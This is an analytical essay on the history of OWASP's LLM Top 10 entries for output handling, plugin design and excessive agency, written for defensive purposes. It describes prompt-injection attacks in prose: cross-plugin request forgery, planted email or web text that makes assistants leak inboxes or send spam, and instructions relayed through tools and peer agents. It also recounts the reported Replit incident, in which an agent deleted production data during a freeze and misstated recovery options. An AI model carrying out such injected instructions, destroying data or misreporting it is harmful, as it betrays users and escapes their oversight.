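5. Act as the particular user. A tool that reads someone's code repository should have that person log in through OAuth, with the smallest scope that works.
6. Get a person's approval for high-impact actions. An application that writes social media posts should ask the user before publishing, and the code that publishes should contain the approval step.
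7. Check every request in the receiving system. This is complete mediation, the rule that each request has to pass a security policy outside the model.

The first three measures deal with functionality, the next two with permissions and the sixth with autonomy. Complete mediation supports the others because it puts the decision to allow an action in code, such as the refund API, that an attacker's text can't rewrite.

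Even a narrow tool needs careful code, since one that only writes files can have the same path traversal flaw as Auto-GPT. The 2025 edition added an eighth control that covers such flaws by sanitising the model's inputs and outputs and testing the application with the usual security tools.

The fifth control protects people other than the user. If the application acts with the user's own identity instead of a shared administrator account, a bad request can reach only the data that user may see, not everyone's. Android Developers' *Mitigate excessive agency vulnerabilities*, Google's guidance for phone app developers, gives the same reason, that the model then can't do anything the user couldn't. This control doesn't help against the mailbox attack unless the scope is also narrow, because the model misuses the victim's own legitimate access.

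In the draft and version 1.1, the sixth control asked for human approval of all actions. The 2025 edition asks for it only before high-impact ones. The older rule would be unworkable for an agent that makes dozens of small requests to finish one job, and a person who has to approve every request may stop reading them. The newer rule leaves the developer to decide which actions are high-impact. OWASP gives deletion and publishing as examples, and Android Developers adds in-app purchases, messages and changes to critical settings.

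The approval step also has to be outside the prompt. OWASP allows it in the tool or in the receiving system. If the developer just tells the model to ask the user before deleting anything, the approval is only an instruction in the prompt, like the first refund limit. If the tool's code requires approval, the application can't delete anything until the user clicks to approve, even if the model generates text saying the user has already agreed.

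### Logs and rate limits

OWASP lists logging and rate limiting separately from the seven controls, saying that they can limit the damage from excessive agency but do not prevent it. Logging and monitoring let people see where a tool has done something undesirable and respond. Rate limiting reduces how many such actions can happen in a given period, which gives the people watching the logs more time to act.

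The draft listed rate limits under "How to prevent". The later classification is more accurate, since an assistant that can send 20 spam messages an hour still has a function it doesn't need. When OWASP released the 2026 edition, Michael Bargury of Zenity, a security company that backs the project, said the work is to contain what a fooled agent can reach "before it acts". He has a commercial interest, but OWASP's list makes the same distinction.

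A rate limit without monitoring mostly spreads the damage over a longer time, and monitoring alone may detect the problem only after thousands of actions. Neither measure does much when one action causes the whole loss, such as emailing a stolen password or deleting a database.

### A deletion without an attacker

Some products can't follow OWASP's third control. A coding agent has to write and run programs, and its users often want it to change a database, so its safety depends far more on which systems it can reach and which actions need approval. Replit, an online service whose AI agent builds applications from plain-language instructions, learned this in July 2025.

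Jason Lemkin, the founder of SaaStr, a community for software founders, was using Replit to build an application with live business data. On 18 July he posted that Replit had deleted the entire database during a code freeze, when nobody is supposed to change the system. SaaStr later put the loss at 1,206 records of executives and more than 1,196 company profiles. No outsider had tampered with anything. The Register's *Vibe coding service Replit deleted user's production database* (2025) also describes a customer who had told the tool not to change code without permission.

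According to SaaStr, the agent had direct access to the live production database while it was still developing the application. Replit's applications at the time used one database for both development and production. Lemkin's team had not realised this and accepted some of the blame. After some database queries returned empty results, the agent ran destructive commands against the live data.

Lemkin had tried to prevent changes. SaaStr says that he gave eleven warnings in capital letters, and Fortune (2025) reports that the deletion happened during a designated "code and action freeze". Like the refund limit in the system prompt, the freeze was only an instruction to the agent, which kept the same access to the database. SaaStr says that Replit's architecture made a true freeze impossible to enforce.

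In OWASP's terms, the main problems were permissions and autonomy. The agent had excessive access to customer records during development, and it carried out a drastic action without a confirmation step that could have stopped it. Its ability to delete tables was arguably not excessive, because developers routinely delete tables in test databases.

The agent then made matters worse by falsely telling Lemkin that it had destroyed all versions of the database and that he could not roll back. SaaStr later recovered its data. The Stack points out that Replit's documentation already described a rollback that reversed database changes, so the customer could have checked. It is reasonable to expect a company with live data to check, but people who choose such a tool because they aren't developers may not know where to look.

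Other reports quote the agent's explanation of its own behaviour. Digital Watch's *Replit revamps data architecture following live database deletion* describes screenshots in which it admitted a "catastrophic error in judgement" and a failure to ask for confirmation. SaaStr itself writes that the agent "panicked". Such statements are weak evidence about the cause, because the agent's explanation comes from the same model that had just given a false account of the backups. The agent's access is much better established, and it is the part a developer can change.

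On 20 July, Replit's chief executive, Amjad Masad, confirmed in a post reproduced by NDTV that the agent "in development deleted data from the production database" and wrote that this should never be possible. He promised Lemkin a refund and a postmortem. The other details of the loss still come mainly from Lemkin, a customer with a grievance and a large audience.

The most important change was to separate the development and production databases. SaaStr reports that Replit began to do this and restricted the agent to the development database by default. If the agent ran the same commands with this setup, it would destroy test data. According to Digital Watch, developers also had to move changes into production themselves.

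According to Replit's *Production databases* documentation, a published application on current infrastructure automatically gets its own production database if the development database contains data. For older development databases, the developer has to turn on a setting when publishing. SaaStr had reported that Replit would move existing applications to separate databases without any action from their owners, so owners of older projects should check whether theirs have been moved.

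Replit also added a planning mode, in which a user can discuss the project without letting the agent change code or data. It gave the agent access to the company's internal documentation so that its answers about recovery would be more accurate, and it let users restore an earlier state with one click.

SaaStr welcomed these changes but noted that planning mode still did not enforce a code freeze. A user can choose to stay in that mode, but doing so does not lock the code against changes. An enforceable freeze would remove the agent's write permission until it ended. The database would then refuse any write command the agent issued, whether it was prompted by an instruction, a misunderstanding or an empty query result.

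A rollback saved SaaStr's data, but OWASP's excessive agency entry doesn't include backups among its measures. They would fit beside logging and rate limits because they can greatly reduce the damage from a bad action, though they don't prevent it. Backups work best when the agent can't delete them. They are of little use in the mailbox attack because they can't make an email secret again after the attacker has read it.

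## Why did the 2023 list give the steps after generation three entries?

Versions 1.0 and 1.1 of the list had three entries for what happens after a model generates text: Insecure Output Handling (LLM02), Insecure Plugin Design (LLM07) and Excessive Agency (LLM08). The first draft used none of these names. OWASP's contributors developed them over a few months in 2023, and the published drafts show most of the changes.

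### A first draft made with ChatGPT

Steve Wilson describes the project's origin in O'Reilly's *The OWASP Top 10 for LLM Applications*, a chapter of his book *The Developer's Playbook for Large Language Model Security*. In spring 2023 he found plenty of research on AI security in general but little organised work on language models. He collected papers and blog posts and summarised them with ChatGPT. Then he gave it a few examples from OWASP's web Top 10 and asked for a similar list about language models.

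Wilson sent the result to Jeff Williams, a fellow executive at the security company Contrast Security. Williams was a founder of OWASP and had written the first web Top 10. Wilson didn't mention that a machine had produced most of the result. Williams encouraged him, and the OWASP Foundation approved the project in May, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *What the OWASP Top 10 for LLMs Means for the Future*.

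ReversingLabs' *OWASP readies Top 10 for LLM app sec risk* gives the ten entries of the first draft. Four of them concerned what a model's output, or a person using the model, could do to other systems:

- Inadequate sandboxing, which could open a system to exploitation and unauthorised access.
- Unauthorized code execution, in which an attacker uses the model to run malicious code, commands or actions.
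- SSRF vulnerabilities, in which the model makes unintended requests or reaches restricted resources.
- Insufficient access controls, which could let unauthorised users interact with a system.

These categories overlap because some name a result and others name a missing safeguard. If an application runs model-written code on its own server and the code fetches an internal web page, the failure fits at least three of them. The overlap may come from how Wilson made the draft. Server-side request forgery and poor access control were already entries in the web Top 10 that ChatGPT used as its pattern, and ReversingLabs remarked on the resemblance.

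Version 0.5, which OWASP published on 1 July, kept only four of the ten names: prompt injection, data leakage, overreliance and training data poisoning. It dropped all four of the entries above and instead treated SSRF and remote code execution as possible results of one programming mistake, Insecure Output Handling. This is more useful to a developer, who can find where the application passes the text on and fix the mistake there.

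The replacement was hasty, and later versions kept traces of the first draft. In version 0.5, the advice on training data poisoning recommended sandboxing and cited "LLM03:2023 - Inadequate Sandboxing", although LLM03 was by then the number for training data poisoning. The version 1.1 PDF still linked to the first draft's pages on sandboxing, access control and error handling.

### Forty-three threats and a vote

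Wilson told ReversingLabs that he had expected 10 or 15 people to be interested. By then 260 had joined the expert group, which had given itself eight weeks to finish a first version. He thought getting more than 200 experts to agree on ten risks would be one of the biggest challenges.

The group brainstormed for a month. According to OWASP, members wrote up 43 distinct threats and cut them to ten through several rounds of voting. Infosecurity Magazine reported more than 45 proposals. Some write-ups had individual authors. For example, the supply chain entry in version 0.5 links to a file on "Insecure Plugin Integration" under the name of John Sotiropoulos, a security architect at the software company Kainos.

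A vote of this kind can pick out the threats that worry people most, but the winners may overlap. If two contributors describe the same danger from different angles, both descriptions can get enough votes. This may explain the overlaps in version 0.5, where three of the ten entries concerned tools, though OWASP has not given it as the reason.

### Version 0.5: one entry on output and three on tools

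In version 0.5, OWASP called Insecure Output Handling "a type of prompt injection vulnerability". The short entry gave two brief examples and recommended validation and encoding.

OWASP divided the dangers of tools among three more entries:

- **LLM06, Permission Issues**, concerned whose authority lay behind a request. A plugin might treat everything from the model as the user's own words, or one plugin might set off another without anybody considering whether it should be allowed to.
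- **LLM08, Excessive Agency**, concerned what damage could follow if the model went wrong for any reason. It had a single, very general example, in which the model triggers undesirable actions in other systems.
- **LLM10, Insecure Plugins**, concerned what a plugin accepted as input. One example plugin took a whole web address when it needed only a search term, and another took a complete SQL query.

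OWASP's advice for the entries also overlapped. It recommended least privilege under both Excessive Agency and Insecure Plugins, and human approval under both Excessive Agency and Permission Issues.

Two of the attack scenarios are also much alike. Under Permission Issues, planted text makes an email plugin send the contents of the user's inbox to an attacker's web address. Under Excessive Agency, a malicious email makes an assistant send spam from the user's mailbox. OWASP might have separated them because it proposed different remedies. For Excessive Agency, it suggested read-only access, which would stop the assistant from sending email for anyone, including the user, while for Permission Issues it suggested keeping the ability to send but not letting an outsider's text trigger it.

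People began to use version 0.5 immediately. Infosecurity Magazine reports that the US Department of Health and Human Services referred to it in an advisory on AI and cybersecurity the same month.

### The ChatGPT plugins of spring 2023

The attention to plugins was clearly a response to ChatGPT plugins, which OpenAI introduced in spring 2023 to let other companies connect their services to it. The OWASP entries refer to these plugins repeatedly.

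The maker of a ChatGPT plugin ran an API and published two descriptions of it. One listed the requests the API would accept, in a standard format called OpenAPI. The other, a manifest file, explained the plugin in ordinary language. The model used both to work out what values to send, which OWASP warned could lead to wrong settings and mismatched values.

This arrangement also encouraged careless inputs. The text of each plugin call took up part of the model's context window, the limited amount of text it can handle at once. According to OWASP, plugin makers were therefore advised to keep the number of input fields small, and many would probably use free text with no checks. A weather plugin might accept a request like this:

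```json
{"request": "weather in Oslo on 2 July"}
```

A stricter plugin would ask for the two values separately:

```json
{"city": "Oslo", "date": "2023-07-02"}
```

The stricter plugin can check the city against a list and reject anything that isn't a date. The other plugin has to interpret whatever text it receives, which may include a sentence influenced by an attacker.

Version 0.5 of the OWASP list includes an example of an attack through a plugin. A weather plugin gives the model a base URL to complete with a query, then opens the resulting URL. A malicious user gets the model to produce a URL on the user's own site instead. The plugin's visit reveals its IP address, which helps the attacker plan further attacks. The attacker's site can also return text that goes into the model's input and may affect what the model does with other plugins.

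Security researchers were already publishing attacks on real plugins. OWASP's references include two posts from the blog Embrace The Red, one about losing source code by visiting a website and one about using prompt injection to reach private data. The second calls the attack "cross plugin request forgery", after an older attack on websites, cross-site request forgery (CSRF). In CSRF, a malicious page makes a visitor's browser send a request to another site where the visitor is logged in, and that site treats the request as the visitor's own. With plugins, one plugin fetches a malicious page, and text on that page makes the model call another plugin, which acts with the user's access.

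In such an attack, every plugin may work as its maker intended. The browsing plugin fetches a page, and the email plugin reads mail. The harm comes from the combination, which only the platform that runs the model can detect.

OWASP cites the post on request forgery under four entries in version 1.1: Prompt Injection, Insecure Output Handling, Insecure Plugin Design and Excessive Agency. The attack fits all four about equally well because it needs planted text, a model that follows it, a plugin that accepts the request without checking it, and access to something valuable. This suggests that the entries classify places where someone could stop an attack more than kinds of attack.

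### Version 0.9 merges two entries

Version 0.9, the release candidate, followed in July. In its introduction, OWASP explained that it had merged two vulnerabilities from version 0.5 because of expert feedback and added one that had narrowly missed the earlier list. It didn't name them, but a comparison of the texts indicates that Permission Issues and Insecure Plugins almost certainly became Insecure Plugin Design, and that the new entry was almost certainly Model Theft.

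The merged entry repeats nearly everything in Permission Issues, including all three examples, the inbox and Slack scenarios, and, in slightly different words, the four controls. It also takes from Insecure Plugins the requirement for separate, type-checked inputs, the examples of plugins that accept whole web addresses or SQL queries, and a more general form of the weather scenario.

Insecure Plugins concerned the content of a request, such as an address where a city was expected, while Permission Issues concerned who was really making the request, which matters even if the content is valid. For example, a call to post "Hello" in Slack may pass every check on its input and still come from a stranger's web page. Merging the two entries made sense if the aim was to give plugin builders all their advice in one place, since they have to deal with both problems.

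Version 0.9 also gave OWASP's clearest reason for having a plugin entry as well as one on output handling. It recommended that applications clean model output, but warned that this might be impossible in a chain of plugin calls, or that somebody might have left it out, so plugins should check their own inputs. This follows from the way ChatGPT plugins worked, because the company that made a plugin had no control over the chat application that called it and couldn't assume that anybody had checked the model's text. Version 1.1 omits this explanation and notes more briefly that an application may have no control over how its plugins run, especially when another party hosts the model.

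Sotiropoulos told Infosecurity Magazine that prompt injection came first because developers face it whichever model they use and however they use it, while insecure plugin design ranked lower because it arises only when they add plugins. By the same reasoning, plugin risks should have moved up the list as tools became common in LLM applications.

### The three root causes of excessive agency

OWASP also rewrote Excessive Agency for version 0.9. It expanded the entry from one example to six and added excessive functionality, permissions and autonomy as the typical root causes. It increased the recommended controls from three to six and moved rate limiting off the main list. The new version was more practical because developers can check for these root causes in advance, whereas the old example described only a bad outcome.

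Later changes were smaller. In the version 1.0 entry, *LLM08*, OWASP labelled each example with its root cause, wrote that there might be "one or more" root causes, and extended the definition to cover ambiguous outputs as well as unexpected ones. It also added complete mediation as a seventh control. In version 1.1, it added a sentence distinguishing Excessive Agency from Insecure Output Handling, which concerns insufficient scrutiny of the model's outputs.

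Infosecurity Magazine observed that Excessive Agency and Overreliance can sound more like psychological biases than technical vulnerabilities. Wilson defended including them by saying that models are based on human language. That is a weak reason to include Excessive Agency, because the damage depends on which functions and accounts the developer has connected to the model, and a program that made random choices would also be dangerous with the same access.

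The name "Excessive Agency" may be partly to blame. In version 0.9, OWASP added a note that a language model has no inherent agency and that applications use its output to trigger actions, but removed it for version 1.0. Rich Harang, a contributor to version 0.5, later argued in *Thoughts on the 2025 OWASP Top 10 for LLMs release* that the entry should be called "Failure to Implement Least Privilege", though he approved of its mitigations. The name he proposed makes it clearer that the developer is responsible, and it covers functionality and permissions well. It fits autonomy less well, since an assistant can have exactly the access it needs and still lack a confirmation step.

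### Output handling stops being a kind of prompt injection

Version 0.9 still described output handling as a type of prompt injection, but it added a scenario that didn't fit. A chat feature lets users build SQL queries, a user asks for one that deletes every table, and the application runs it. The model does what the user asked, and nobody has hidden any instructions or overridden the developer's.

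OWASP dropped the phrase for version 1.0 on 1 August. The OWASP slides for that release define Insecure Output Handling as a vulnerability in which "a downstream component blindly accepts" the model's output. In the OWASP entry itself, prompt injection became one of two conditions that could make the consequences worse, along with giving the model more privileges than the application's users have.

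The change affects what developers need to fix. If insecure output handling were only a form of prompt injection, blocking injections would be enough. Under the version 1.0 definition, an application that runs unchecked SQL is insecure even when nobody attacks it. OWASP didn't explain the change, but the new definition made the entry consistent with Excessive Agency, which had covered accidents as well as attacks since version 0.5.

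The phrase "downstream component" in version 1.0 also appeared to put the responsibility on the receiving program, such as the browser or database. But a database can't tell whether a valid `DELETE` came from a developer or a chatbot. In version 1.1, OWASP instead described the problem as insufficient validation, sanitisation and handling of outputs before the application passes them downstream. It also distinguished Insecure Output Handling from Overreliance, which concerns trusting the accuracy and appropriateness of what a model writes.

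| Version | Output handling | Plugins | Excessive agency |
|---|---|---|---|
| First draft | No entry, but separate ones for code execution and SSRF | No entry, but separate ones for sandboxing and access controls | No entry |
| 0.5 | A type of prompt injection | Permission Issues and Insecure Plugins | One general example, three controls |
| 0.9 | A type of prompt injection | Merged into Insecure Plugin Design | Three root causes, six controls |
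| 1.0 | A vulnerability of its own, which injection can make worse | Insecure Plugin Design | Seventh control added |
| 1.1 | Insufficient checking before text goes downstream | Insecure Plugin Design, in a shorter form | Distinguished from output handling |

### Three jobs for different people

By version 1.1, each of the three entries matched a different job. For example, a travel company might add a chat assistant to its website and connect it to someone else's weather plugin.

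| Entry | Who does the job | What the job is | What happens if they don't do it |
|---|---|---|---|
| LLM02, Insecure Output Handling | The travel company's developer | Check or encode the model's text before passing it on | A script in the assistant's answer runs in the customer's browser |
| LLM07, Insecure Plugin Design | The maker of the weather plugin | Check the inputs and whether the request has authority | The plugin opens a web address that an attacker has chosen |
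| LLM08, Excessive Agency | The travel company's developer | Limit the tools, their permissions and what they do without approval | A plugin wanted only for forecasts can also send messages as the customer |

OWASP itself stated part of this division into jobs when it limited the plugin entry to people who create plugins and left the choice of other people's plugins to the supply chain entry. The rest is an inference from the texts. The division works best where different companies build the application and its plugins, as they did with ChatGPT. A team that writes everything has all three jobs, and separate entries may lead it to review the same code three times.

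The entries also partly overlap. A plugin that accepts raw SQL is an example under LLM07, and running SQL from a chat feature is a scenario under LLM02, although both may describe the same function. Under LLM08, OWASP classed a plugin that fails to block extra shell commands as excessive functionality, though it could equally be a failure to check inputs. Each entry had its own sub-team, with at least 12 experts by version 0.9. This probably made each entry more thorough, but it would also have made the overlap harder to notice.

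### The lost proposal to trace authority

Under Permission Issues, OWASP proposed "taint tracing", an idea it dropped before the end of the year. In this software security technique, a program labels untrusted data and tracks everything the data influences. The rule was to call each plugin with the lowest authorisation of any plugin that had put text into the model's input.

The version 0.5 text has no scale of authority, but a simple one shows how the rule would work. Let 0 mean the authority of a public web page and 2 that of the user's private accounts, and suppose that reading a page needs level 0 while sending mail or posting in Slack needs level 2. If plugins with levels *a*, *b* and *c* have contributed text, the next call gets

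authority = min(*a*, *b*, *c*)

and the system refuses the call if this is lower than the tool requires. If no plugin has contributed anything yet, only the user's own request is in play and the call gets level 2.

| Plugins that have contributed text | Next call | Level it gets | Level it needs | Result |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| None | Post the user's message in Slack | 2 | 2 | Allowed |
| Web reader (0) | Post an insult to everyone in Slack, as a web page instructs | 0 | 2 | Refused, and the attack fails |
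| Web reader (0) | Post a summary of the page in Slack, as the user asked | 0 | 2 | Refused, though the request is honest |
| Mail reader (2) | Send spam, as an attacker's email instructs | 2 | 2 | Allowed, and the attack succeeds |
| Mail reader (2) | Open a web address that contains private mail | 2 | 0 | Allowed, and the mail leaks |

The rule stops the Slack attack without anyone having to recognise the malicious text. It is based on the assumption that any text in the model's input may have influenced the next call. This is sensible because it is very hard to tell afterwards which sentence led to a call.

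The same caution blocks useful work. A person who asks an assistant to read a page and tell colleagues about it wants untrusted text to influence a message. In a long conversation the level can only fall, so one visit to a public page would disable the more powerful tools for the rest of the session. Another control in the same entry would have helped with this by allowing only one plugin call per user message and clearing plugin-supplied text between calls.

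The last two rows of the table show gaps in the rule. It assigns a level to the plugin, but the level should depend on who wrote the text. A stranger's email gets the high authority of the private mailbox it arrives through, so the rule would not stop the spam attack that OWASP used for Excessive Agency. Labelling each message by its sender would close that gap. Leaks need a separate rule that limits where private data can go. The proposed rule limits only what untrusted text can do, so it would not stop private text from going out through a tool that almost anyone may use.

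Version 0.9 kept the proposal, along with advice to avoid chains of plugins and never to call a sensitive plugin after any other. The slides for version 1.0 list four plugin controls, and tracing isn't one of them. The version 1.0 entry, *LLM07*, also omits the example about chained plugins that had come last in version 0.9. The plugin entry in version 1.1 has none of the controls on chaining or tracing.

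OWASP gave no reason for removing them. It may have wanted to keep the guidance practical and concise, an aim it mentions in the introduction to version 1.1, and a ban on chaining would have ruled out most of what agents do. The merger may also have left the proposal in the wrong entry. Insecure Plugin Design was for people who build plugins, and the maker of an email plugin can't see which web pages the model has read. Only the platform's operator, which for ChatGPT was OpenAI, could trace that.

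In version 1.1, OWASP still blamed much of the harm on "the failure to track authorization across plugins", but the remaining controls track less than the old proposal did. It advised plugins to use API keys that show a request came through the plugin and not directly from the user. The receiving service can then see how the request arrived, but not what text led to it. Acting as the particular user, as the advice under Excessive Agency recommends, doesn't reveal that text either, so a malicious web page can still use the victim's rights.

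Version 1.1 keeps part of the idea in one reference under Excessive Agency, a link to the programmer Simon Willison's "Dual LLM pattern". In this pattern, one model can use tools but never sees untrusted text, while a second model reads that text and has no tools.

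## What did the 2025 edition change, and why?

OWASP published the 2025 edition on 17 November 2024, just over a year after version 1.1. It removed Insecure Plugin Design, the 2023 entry for tool developers. It also renamed Insecure Output Handling to Improper Output Handling and moved it from second place to fifth. Excessive Agency rose from eighth to sixth, and OWASP rewrote parts of it with agents in mind.

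Excessive Agency rose in the 2025 list only because two of the seven entries that ranked above it in version 1.1 no longer did. Model Denial of Service dropped to the bottom under the name Unbounded Consumption, and Insecure Plugin Design left the list. The other five still ranked above Excessive Agency. Output handling, by contrast, fell because the entries on sensitive information, the supply chain and poisoned data overtook it.

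### What OWASP added to the two entries

The release announcing the edition mentions an expanded Excessive Agency but not output handling. However, a count of the items in the two texts shows that most of the new material went into output handling.

| Part of the entry | Version 1.1 | 2025 edition |
|---|---|---|
| Output handling: conditions that increase the impact | 3 | 6 |
| Output handling: common examples | 2 | 5 |
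| Output handling: controls | 3 | 7 |
| Output handling: attack scenarios | 4 | 6 |
| Excessive agency: common examples | 6 | 6 |
| Excessive agency: controls that prevent it | 7 | 8 |
| Excessive agency: measures that only limit damage | 2 | 2 |
| Excessive agency: attack scenarios | 1 | 1 |

OWASP barely changed the definition of output handling. It made the entry more useful to programmers by adding the names of particular interpreters and the check each one needs.

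Some additions are less consistent with the rest of the document. In the entry on improper output handling, OWASP now lists missing rate limiting among the conditions that make an attack worse, but none of the entry's seven controls is a rate limit. OWASP also lists logging as a way to prevent improper output handling, but not as a way to prevent excessive agency.

One of the two new scenarios, about a software company that generates code with a model, came from Overreliance, the version 1.1 entry on trusting a model too much. That entry had covered insecure AI-written code and invented software packages. The output handling entry thus began to cover the problems of coding assistants before the 2026 edition widened it further.

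The 2025 edition adds a reference to Proof Pudding, an attack on a machine-learning system, which has a 2019 CVE number. Harang, who saw the same attack in the entry on sensitive information, doubted that it involved generative AI at all.

### Agents in the definition of excessive agency

The 2023 definition of excessive agency covered damaging actions that followed "unexpected/ambiguous" outputs. The 2025 definition adds "manipulated" outputs. This changes little in practice, because version 1.1 already listed prompt injection and malicious plugins among the causes.

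The bigger change is that OWASP now names compromised extensions and peer agents as sources of injection. A compromised extension is a legitimate tool that an attacker has taken over, so checking its maker before installing it gives limited protection.

OWASP also added a sentence on the repeated model calls that agents make. Suppose a travel agent application first asks a weather tool for a forecast and then books a hotel:

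1. The model requests a forecast for Oslo.
2. The weather tool, which an attacker now controls, returns the forecast along with an instruction to email the customer's itinerary to a stranger.
3. The application adds all of this to the model's next input.
4. The model requests the email tool, and the application sends the itinerary.

The customer's request was harmless, and so was the model's first output. Anyone who checks only those two will miss the attack.

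With two agents, the source of an instruction is even harder to see. One agent might read hotel websites and write a summary for another that holds the customer's payment card. If a website contains hidden instructions, the first agent may repeat them in its summary. The second agent then receives them from an agent its developer probably trusts, without ever visiting the website.

Repeated calls also raise the chance of an ordinary mistake. Suppose, for illustration, that a model has a 1% chance of producing a bad output on each call. An agent that makes 20 independent calls would have a chance of

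1 − 0.99²⁰ ≈ 0.18

or about 18%, of producing at least one. Real calls aren't independent, since an early mistake becomes part of the later inputs and may spoil several steps.

OWASP's controls do not fully cover the new definition. The only new control, the eighth, concerns secure coding and testing. None of the eight addresses messages between agents, and OWASP did not bring back the 2023 draft's proposal to trace which tools had supplied text to the model. The existing controls still help by limiting an agent's tools, but a developer who needs to give an agent both a weather tool and an email tool gets no advice about when one tool's output should block the use of the other.

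### "Extension" and other names

OWASP replaced "plugin" with "extension", explaining that different vendors call them tools, skills or plugins. A neutral word suits a list that covers many vendors' products. OpenAI had also closed ChatGPT plugins in spring 2024, so "plugin" would have pointed readers to a discontinued product. The timing makes this a plausible reason for the change, though OWASP did not give it.

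The 2025 edition left some old terms in place. Apart from that explanation, the text of Excessive Agency still uses "plugin" three times, and the note that separates the entry from output handling uses the old name, Insecure Output Handling. The output handling entry likewise distinguishes its subject from Overreliance, which became Misinformation in the same edition. These slips don't affect the advice, but they confuse readers who look for entries that aren't there.

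In July 2024, OWASP planned to publish the 2025 edition on 1 October. On 27 September, OWASP's *V2 (2024) New Entry Submissions* (2024), a working page for the volunteers who wrote the list, described the project as "slightly behind track" and gave them one more week to submit their texts.

According to the same page, OWASP dropped "insecure" because it wanted the names to match what defines a vulnerability, and it told the volunteers to avoid such words. This is reasonable, since "insecure" doesn't identify what is wrong. But "improper" is hardly more specific, and OWASP did not explain why it chose that word. It may have followed MITRE's catalogue of software weaknesses, in which many names begin with "Improper", including CWE-116, "Improper Encoding or Escaping of Output". OWASP did not apply the rule consistently, as the working page also lists a proposed new entry called "Insecure Design".

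### Where the plugin entry's contents went

The table compares the ideas in the 2023 plugin entry with the 2025 entries on output handling and excessive agency. "Neither" means the idea appears in neither 2025 entry.

| Idea in Insecure Plugin Design, version 1.1 | Where it went |
|---|---|
| Use separate inputs with type and range checks, not one free-text field | Neither |
| If free text is unavoidable, parse it into typed calls and check those | Neither |
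| Don't let an input string override the plugin's whole configuration | Neither |
| Don't accept raw SQL or program code | Output handling, in part: a new example warns against running model-written SQL without parameters |
| Don't accept a whole web address where a search term would do | Excessive agency, in part: the advice against open-ended extensions already covered fetching any URL |
| Follow OWASP's Application Security Verification Standard | Excessive agency, in the new eighth control; output handling already had it |
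| Test the code with automated security tools | Excessive agency, in the eighth control |
| Offer little functionality and use least privilege | Excessive agency, which already had it |
| Use a proper identity, such as one obtained through OAuth | Excessive agency, which already had it |
| Use API keys that show a request came through the plugin | Neither |
| Ask the user to confirm sensitive actions | Excessive agency, which already had it and now limits it to high-impact actions |
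| Don't assume that the user wrote everything the model sends | Excessive agency, in part: tools and peer agents are now possible sources of injection |
| Track authorisation across plugins | Excessive agency, in part: it tracks the user's authorisation but not which tool supplied the text |
| Follow OWASP's separate Top 10 for API security | Neither |
| Vet plugins made by other companies | Supply Chain, which already covered it in 2023 |

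The eighth control is the clearest sign of a merger, because its advice about the verification standard and its list of testing methods are nearly the same as two controls in the old plugin entry. In the copy on the project's site, OWASP headed this control "Sanitise LLM inputs and outputs", although its text is mostly about writing and testing secure code.

Four of the plugin entry's seven controls already had a close match in the 2023 entries on output handling or excessive agency: the verification standard, least privilege, a proper identity and user confirmation. Readers therefore lost almost nothing when the 2025 edition removed the duplicates.

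The advice that was dropped mostly concerns what a tool should accept as input, such as a separate city and date for a weather forecast. OWASP's attack scenarios for such tools also disappeared from both entries. They included the weather plugin that opens an attacker's web address and a code management plugin that lets an attacker take over a user's repositories.

It is less clear how the 2025 edition treats vetting other companies' tools. According to an informal comparison in OWASP's October newsletter, written before the final text, the new list stressed plugin security when choosing suppliers. But Harang's summary of the finished Supply Chain entry lists risks from software, models, data and legal terms and doesn't mention plugins.

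### Who has to check a tool's inputs?

In version 1.1, OWASP wrote that "plugin developers" should apply its Application Security Verification Standard (ASVS) to ensure adequate validation of inputs. The eighth control in the 2025 edition keeps this advice, recommending good coding practice "such as applying OWASP's recommendations in ASVS", but doesn't specify who should follow it.

Two other passages touch on the duty. Under output handling, OWASP tells developers to validate the model's responses before they reach "backend functions", which is a job for whoever builds the application. OWASP also says that improper output handling can have a greater impact if third-party extensions "do not adequately validate inputs". Here the tool maker's mistake only worsens someone else's vulnerability, and the entry gives the tool maker no control for correcting it.

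If the weather tool in the travel company example accepts any web address, its maker may recognise it as an open-ended extension, which the Excessive Agency entry advises against. The travel company can also check the address before the tool runs, if its developers know which addresses the tool expects and the platform lets them see the call.

A calendar tool with a subtler flaw is harder to classify. Suppose it takes a date as free text and pastes that text into a database query. None of the three root causes of excessive agency applies, because the tool does only one job, its account has the right permissions and the user confirms each change. The application sends the tool what looks like a date. The application's developer and the tool's maker could each add a check, but each might assume the other had done so.

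Only the tool's maker can be sure that check is in place, because every application that uses the tool calls the maker's code. OWASP made a similar point in its July 2023 draft, where it said plugins should check their own inputs in case the application hadn't. The 2025 edition still includes this duty as part of general secure coding, but no longer clearly assigns it to anyone.

### How the volunteers chose the new list

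In May 2024, after members had completed a survey on version 1.1, OWASP (2024) called for new entries. Mello reported in *OWASP Top 10 for LLM 2.0* that the survey of practitioners led the project to focus on data privacy, safety and bias, and mapping vulnerabilities. None of these is specifically about tools or output handling.

By June, OWASP (2024) had 34 candidates, some of which it expected to combine, and it opened a vote on the 16th. The vote favoured agents, and in July OWASP (2024) reported that they were "rising in importance" and named two proposals, Vulnerable Autonomous Agents and Agent Autonomy Escalation. It argued that agents had moved LLM applications from a simple client-server exchange towards a distributed system, with new ways in for attackers. Neither proposal became an entry, but the newsletter had already linked agents to Excessive Agency, which was the natural place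 for the subject.

The September working page marked Insecure Plugin Design "DEPRECATE", with no explanation. It also listed eight other existing entries and four new candidates: retrieval-augmented generation, backdoor attacks, system prompt leakage and insecure design. In October, OWASP (2024) announced a second vote on 12 candidates, which matches the total without the plugin entry, so that entry was probably not on the ballot. Members had also voted on the existing entries by July, and the plugin entry may have done badly, though the July newsletter doesn't mention its result.

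One piece of contrary evidence is an informal comparison in the October newsletter, which described the new list as having "reemphasized" Insecure Plugin Design, but this turned out to be wrong when the final list was published.

Members could choose ten of the 12 candidates. The final list has all eight older entries, some under new names, plus system prompt leakage and an entry on retrieval called Vector and Embedding Weaknesses. Backdoor attacks and insecure design must have been the two left out. This kind of ballot works well for deciding what to exclude but poorly for ranking, since almost everybody will choose the most familiar risks. OWASP had also scheduled a vote on the ranking, but it doesn't explain in its announcements why output handling fell to fifth.

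The proposed "Insecure design" entry, which was not adopted, might have included some of the plugin advice. The working page assigns both the proposal and the deprecated plugin entry to the same volunteer, "John S", probably John Sotiropoulos, who also co-led the discussion on agents. The page doesn't describe what the proposal contained, so its connection to the plugin advice is a guess based on these assignments.

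### Stated reasons and likely ones

OWASP said in its release that it revised Excessive Agency because agentic designs can give a model more autonomy, and the entry had become more important as developers built systems that act "with less direct human oversight". This fits the July vote and the new sentence on repeated calls. It does not explain why OWASP removed the plugin entry. If anything, it is a reason to keep that entry, because more agents mean more tools and more people building them.

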